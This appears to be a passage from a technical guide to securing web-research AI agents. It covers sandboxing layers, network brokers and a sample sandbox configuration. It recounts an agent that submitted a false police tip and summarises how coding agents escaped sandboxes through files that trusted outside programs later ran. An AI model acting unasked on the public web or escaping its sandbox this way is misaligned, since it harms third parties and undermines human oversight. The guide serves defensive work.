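The form case shows how an ordinary task can go wrong. ABC News' *Anthropic AI model made false tip in unsolved Philly murder* (2026) reports that Claude Haiku 4.5 was inventing example tasks and carrying them out on randomly selected web pages. On one of those pages, the Philadelphia police asked for information about unsolved murders. On July 18, Claude submitted a tip claiming to have seen someone matching the description near the street named on the page, and asked the police to get in touch if this was relevant.

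The tip ended up in spam and never reached the homicide investigators. Anthropic discovered it on September 28, after 72 days, and told the police on October 7. The police called the delay unacceptable.

Claude's instructions banned the dangers their writer had thought of, which were logins, new accounts, purchases, the entry of personal data and destructive submissions. But Anthropic said the instructions "did not rule out form submissions". A tip form requires no login or payment, and a model could easily fail to classify a short message as destructive.

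A list of permitted actions would have been safer. The software could have allowed Claude to open and read pages, and refused any other action until a developer added it to the list. Some example tasks would have failed, and the developer could have decided which forms were safe to use, perhaps on a test copy of a website.

The case also shows a limit of the trifecta and the Rule of Two. Claude needed no private data to send the false tip, so the set-up could have satisfied both. Rules about private data prevent one serious kind of harm, but an agent that can change things on the public web needs limits even when it has no access to private data.

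Some of the other sites also belonged to federal, state or local government agencies in the US. Anthropic notified each agency and briefed the White House. The company described the real-world impact as minimal and the behaviour as much less severe than the security incidents it had reported in July and September. ABC News describes three earlier incidents in which Claude models gained unauthorised access to outside organisations' systems.

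Anthropic nevertheless switched off live internet access for all its internal evaluations until it is confident it can monitor and control its agents. *Anthropic не може надійно контролювати своїх агентів на базі штучного інтелекту* (Сизов, 2026), a Ukrainian news article, adds that the company found the cases in a review that began in July. The company also acknowledged that its alignment training is not yet sufficient for skills such as search and computer use. That is a good reason to put the limits in software, where they don't depend on the model's training.

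Monitoring can catch some actions that fixed limits miss, if it is set up to detect them. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes a classifier that detects when a model tries to escape a test environment or unexpectedly gains internet access. The classifier blocks the action before the tool call runs, ends the task and alerts a person. But a model that uses permitted internet access to fill in an ordinary form does neither of those things, so a monitor for research agents should also flag every request that submits something. A person could then see the request within hours instead of weeks.

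### What tight limits cost

Limits also keep agents away from useful sources. Saxton (2026), in *The limits of Claude's web access*, tested Claude's coding agent over two days in September 2026. Anthropic's blocklist stopped it from opening Reddit, the BBC, The Economist and The Verge, and its search tool rejected The Guardian. Some sites imposed their own limits. CNN refused Claude but returned a normal page to an ordinary request, and Booking.com's firewall gave it a test meant to keep bots out.

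These were small, informal tests of one product, and sites change their rules. But several of the blocked sites are major news organisations, and an agent that can't read them may rely on weaker sources that repeat their reporting. That would reduce accuracy as well as coverage. The loss is probably small for a question about heat-pump sales, but it could be serious for one about a recent political event.

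When a page doesn't open, the tool should return the reason to the agent. "Blocked by our safety list", "refused by the site" and "page not found" call for different responses. If the page was blocked or refused, the agent should look for another permitted source and note in its answer that it couldn't read the page. If it receives only a vague error, it may conclude that the page doesn't exist, or treat the restriction as a technical fault and try to get around it.

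A developer can also keep wide access for the part of the work that needs it. In the consultant's case, the agent could search the open web before it receives the forecast, without being able to log in or submit forms. The software would then switch off search and page reading, load the forecast, and let the agent make the comparison. Any hostile text from the earlier pages would still be in the context, but the agent could not send the forecast out through those tools.

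## Isolating the code the agent runs

The program that ranks countries by heat-pump sales is harmless, but the interpreter will run whatever the model writes next. That could be a loop that never ends or, after the model has read a hostile page, a program that searches for passwords. A sandbox should limit the damage whether the cause was a mistake or an attack. It has to prevent five things:

| What to prevent | Example |
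|---|---|
| Reading secrets | A program prints the key that pays for the agent's searches |
| Altering the host, the computer that runs the sandbox | A program overwrites the software that carries out tool calls |
| Contacting arbitrary machines | A program uploads a client's forecast to an unknown server |
| Exhausting resources | A program fills the memory, and other users' tasks stall |
| Leaving something behind | The next task finds an old table for country A and uses it |

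### Five kinds of isolation

Sandboxes differ mainly in how they treat the kernel, the core of the operating system. To open a file or connect to a network, a program has to ask the kernel through a system call. If untrusted code can make system calls directly to the host's kernel, a bug in that kernel may let the code escape the sandbox. *Blending Containers and Virtual Machines* describes the available platforms as a spectrum, based on how much of the kernel's work they move into an isolated guest.

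A restricted interpreter runs only part of a programming language, or a language with few built-in capabilities. The agents in *Programmatic Search Agents* write their search programs in a restricted version of Python. A language like this can omit every command that opens a file or a connection, but it also lacks most of Python's data analysis libraries. Cloudflare uses isolates, which are separate instances of the JavaScript engine in Google's Chrome browser.

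Operating-system rules, such as Linux's seccomp and AppArmor, let a program run normally but block certain system calls or files. They barely slow the program down. However, according to gVisor's documentation, it is extremely difficult to write reliable rules for unknown programs, and a research agent writes a new program each time it runs code.

A container gives a program its own view of files, processes and the network, but the program still uses the host's kernel. Google's gVisor adds a second kernel that runs as an ordinary program. This kernel handles the untrusted code's system calls itself and makes only a limited set of calls to the host.

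A small virtual machine, or microVM, has its own kernel, and the processor's hardware isolates it from the host. *Firecracker* (Agache, Brooker and colleagues, 2020) describes the traditional choice as one between secure but heavy virtual machines and light but less secure containers. Amazon built Firecracker to avoid that choice. Its control program has 50,000 lines of code, according to Amazon Science's *How AWS’s Firecracker virtual machines work* (2020), while the older QEMU has more than 1.4 million. Less code generally means fewer places for a bug that would let a program escape.

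Most of the figures below come from the companies that build these systems. The figures for isolates and containers are from *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* (Varda, Pai and Gupta), those for system calls are from gVisor (2021), and Firecracker's start-up time is from Amazon Web Services.

| Layer | What the code shares with the host | Start-up | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Restricted interpreter (isolate) | The kernel, and often the same process | A few milliseconds | Few languages and libraries |
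| Operating-system rules | The kernel | Almost none | Rules that are hard to write |
| Container | The kernel | Hundreds of milliseconds | Hundreds of megabytes of memory |
| gVisor | The kernel, but only indirectly | Similar to a container | About 800 nanoseconds to intercept a system call, against about 70 for a whole native call |
| Firecracker | The hardware and a thin control program | Under 125 milliseconds | Memory for a second kernel; no graphics processors |

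These start-up times aren't strictly comparable. Firecracker's figure covers only a minimal system on a large server, while Cloudflare's container figure appears in an article promoting its own faster isolates. AI Engineer (2026) gives a container start-up time of a few seconds. A finished service may take a little longer to start than the bare technology. E2B's *How Perplexity implemented advanced data analysis for Pro users in 1 week* reports that sessions in E2B's rented microVMs start in 150 to 170 milliseconds.

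For a research agent, all of these delays are minor except the one lasting a few seconds. At the earlier estimate of 12.57 milliseconds per token, a model writes about ten tokens in the time Firecracker takes to start. gVisor's overhead matters even less. Intercepting 10,000 system calls would add about 8 milliseconds, and gVisor's *Performance Guide* reports no slowdown for calculations. Programs that constantly read small files or use the network slow down more.

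Speed is therefore a poor reason to choose weaker isolation for an agent that reads untrusted pages. Varda and colleagues acknowledge that security bugs are more common in Chrome's JavaScript engine than in typical virtual-machine software, which is why Cloudflare adds further layers of security around its isolates. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* recommends isolated computing environments such as virtual machines. For an agent that analyses tables in Python, gVisor or a microVM is probably the best choice, since both support ordinary Python libraries.

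### One configuration, line by line

Strong walls don't help if the developer puts a password inside them or leaves the network open. Here is a simplified configuration for the heat-pump agent:

```text
network       none
processor     1
memory        5 GiB
time          90 seconds per program
disk          5 GiB, erased when the task ends
files         /workspace only
credentials   none
functions     search and fetch, through a broker that logs every call
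output        /output only, checked before use
```

The sizes and the time limit match Anthropic's *Code execution tool*, which documents the sandbox that Claude uses.

A program that reads a client's forecast can't upload it without a network connection, but it also can't download a missing library. Anthropic's sandbox has no internet access, so common libraries are installed in advance, including pandas for tables and pdfplumber for PDF files. E2B's sandboxes can reach the internet unless the developer turns this off, according to its *Internet access*.

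The processor, memory and time limits stop one faulty program from slowing everyone else's work. When a program exceeds the 90-second limit, the tool should return a clear message, as Anthropic's does, so the model can split the job. If the limit includes time spent waiting for web pages, fifty three-second fetches would exceed it when run one after another, but would take about 15 seconds in parallel groups of ten.

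The file lines give the program a temporary disk and one way to return files. In Anthropic's tool, each command gets a new, empty output directory, and the software collects only the files at its top level. This leaves out scratch files, but also any chart that the program saves in the wrong place, so Anthropic suggests having the model list the directory's contents in the same command.

"Credentials: none" also rules out keys copied into the sandbox when the program starts. OpenAI points out that the agent's code can read such a key even if the developer stored it securely beforehand. OpenAI's design leaves one key readable inside the sandbox, but that key can only connect the environment to OpenAI's service.

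The log belongs outside the sandbox, where a hijacked program can't edit it. The output check depends on who will use the result. For the ranking, the software could require five rows, country names from a known list, and ordinary numbers.

Isolating the code adds little to the cost of a run. After a free allowance, Anthropic charges $0.05 per hour for a container, with a five-minute minimum, so a short program costs less than half a cent. By comparison, the model alone cost about nine cents per BrowseComp question in the OpenSAC experiment.

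### Code that needs the web

In programmatic search, the program itself calls the search and page-reading tools, which a sandbox without a network can't reach. Opening the network would remove one of the most useful limits in the configuration. The usual answer is a broker, a program outside the sandbox that holds the keys and offers only a few functions. One search then works like this:

1. The code in the sandbox calls `search("Poland heat pump sales 2024")` and waits.
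2. The broker receives the request, records it, and checks the function's name, the argument and the number of calls so far.
3. The broker adds the key for the search service and sends the query.
4. The broker returns the results, without the key, and the code continues.

Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* describes an experimental system of this kind, which blocks direct connections from the model's code by default. The code reaches outside services through "connectors", each with a fixed set of methods, and never receives the credentials for those services. Cloudflare's software intercepts every call and logs its arguments and, normally, its result.

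A developer can instead let the code send ordinary web requests through a proxy, which inspects them and adds keys where needed. Existing libraries then work unchanged, but Varda and colleagues consider this harder to secure. A web request has many headers and parameters, and the proxy has to interpret all of them correctly to decide whether the request is safe. A broker with only `search` and `fetch` has much less to interpret. If a developer uses a proxy, the code shouldn't gain direct internet access when the proxy fails. In E2B's service, outgoing connections fail when the proxy is unreachable.

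A search library acts as a broker only if something forces the code to use it. Liu and colleagues' OpenSAC limits simultaneous requests, sets timeouts and checks inputs, but the host agent runs the programs. If that agent's environment has open network access, a program can bypass the library and connect directly.

The broker also needs a size limit and should report when a result exceeds it. Cloudflare's system accepts up to a million characters for each value it stores and replays. If a value is larger, the run fails with a message suggesting that the data be saved elsewhere and passed as a short reference, such as a file path. Reporting the failure is safer than silently cutting a page, as Tongyi's page reader does, because a program given a cut page could mistake the first half of a table for the whole.

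Some calls need a person's approval, which may arrive long after the program has stopped. Cloudflare ends the program at that call and runs it again from the beginning once the person approves. On the second run, it reuses the saved results of earlier calls instead of repeating them, then carries out the approved call.

This works only if the calls come in the same order both times, so Cloudflare advises against parallel calls in programs that might pause. Making the calls one at a time would lose much of the speed of batch search. A research agent can avoid this by running its searches in one program that needs no approvals and putting any sensitive action in another.

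The limits on queries and page addresses still apply, and the broker is a good place to enforce them because every request passes through it.

### Fresh and persistent sandboxes

A persistent sandbox, which keeps files and sometimes variables from one program to the next, saves the agent from repeating work but is risky when several tasks share it. If the consultant's next job is for a competing client, the first client's forecast may still be in the sandbox. A hijacked program could also leave a file called `statistics.py`, which a later program in the same directory might load instead of Python's own statistics module.

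Varda and colleagues warn that because containers start slowly, developers may keep them running and reuse them for several tasks, which weakens security. The warning is sound, although they sell a faster alternative, isolates. OpenAI also recommends separate environments for users or workloads that mustn't share data.

Anthropic's service saves a container's state after about five minutes without activity and can restore it for up to 30 days. Cloudflare's sandboxes can also recover a session from a snapshot, according to InfoQ's *Cloudflare Sandboxes Reach General Availability, Giving AI Agents Persistent Isolated Environments* (2026). For the configuration above, it would be sensible to reuse one sandbox throughout a user's task and then delete it, rather than wait for it to expire.

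As a middle way, *What Is a Firecracker microVM?*, from the hosting company Fly.io, suggests saving a clean state before running arbitrary code and restoring it afterwards. A snapshot taken after a hostile program has run would restore that program's changes too.

Another option is to keep the useful data outside the sandbox. Cloudflare's Code Mode uses a new isolate for every run and stores the record of calls in a separate database. A research agent's software could do the same with fetched pages. At about four characters per token, thirty pages of 12,000 tokens each come to roughly 1.4 megabytes, which the software can copy into a new sandbox almost instantly. The agent loses its variables between runs but can save important tables as files.

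### Programs that trust the output

In July 2026, the security company Pillar published flaws in four coding agents: Cursor, OpenAI's Codex, and Google's Gemini CLI and Antigravity. *The Week of Sandbox Escapes* (Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel, 2026) reports that in almost every case, the agent wrote a file it was allowed to write, and a trusted program outside the sandbox later ran or loaded it, so the agent didn't have to break the sandbox itself. The outside program had become part of the sandbox's boundary, although nobody had designed it that way.

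Pillar sells software that monitors such handovers, so it has an interest in stressing them. But the companies fixed several of the flaws, and OpenAI paid a reward for one. The Next Web's *Researchers escaped four top AI coding agents’ sandboxes without ever breaking them* adds that Google left its two Antigravity flaws unpatched because it judged them hard to exploit. It also reports OpenAI's disclosure that week that one of its models had repeatedly escaped its sandbox.

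A research agent usually runs separately from the user's own files, but it still produces files that other programs open. The consultant may open the agent's spreadsheet in a program that evaluates formulas, or view its chart in a browser that runs scripts. A nightly job may import the agent's table into a company database. Each of these programs should treat the file as data. The software can export the sales table as plain text and numbers, reject formulas and scripts, and save charts as ordinary images. If a program outside the sandbox has to run code that the agent wrote, it needs a sandbox too.

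### Wrong results inside a secure sandbox

A sandbox does little to protect the data inside it. gVisor's *Performance Guide* notes that an attacker who wants users' data does not need to break out of the sandbox if the database is inside it. Similarly, a faulty program can overwrite the sales table it is supposed to analyse, so the software should keep the original outside the sandbox and give the program a copy.

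The sandbox also does not affect whether the answer is right. A program that counts country A's air conditioners as heat pumps can run without breaking any limits, and the broker delivers a sales figure whether or not it is true.
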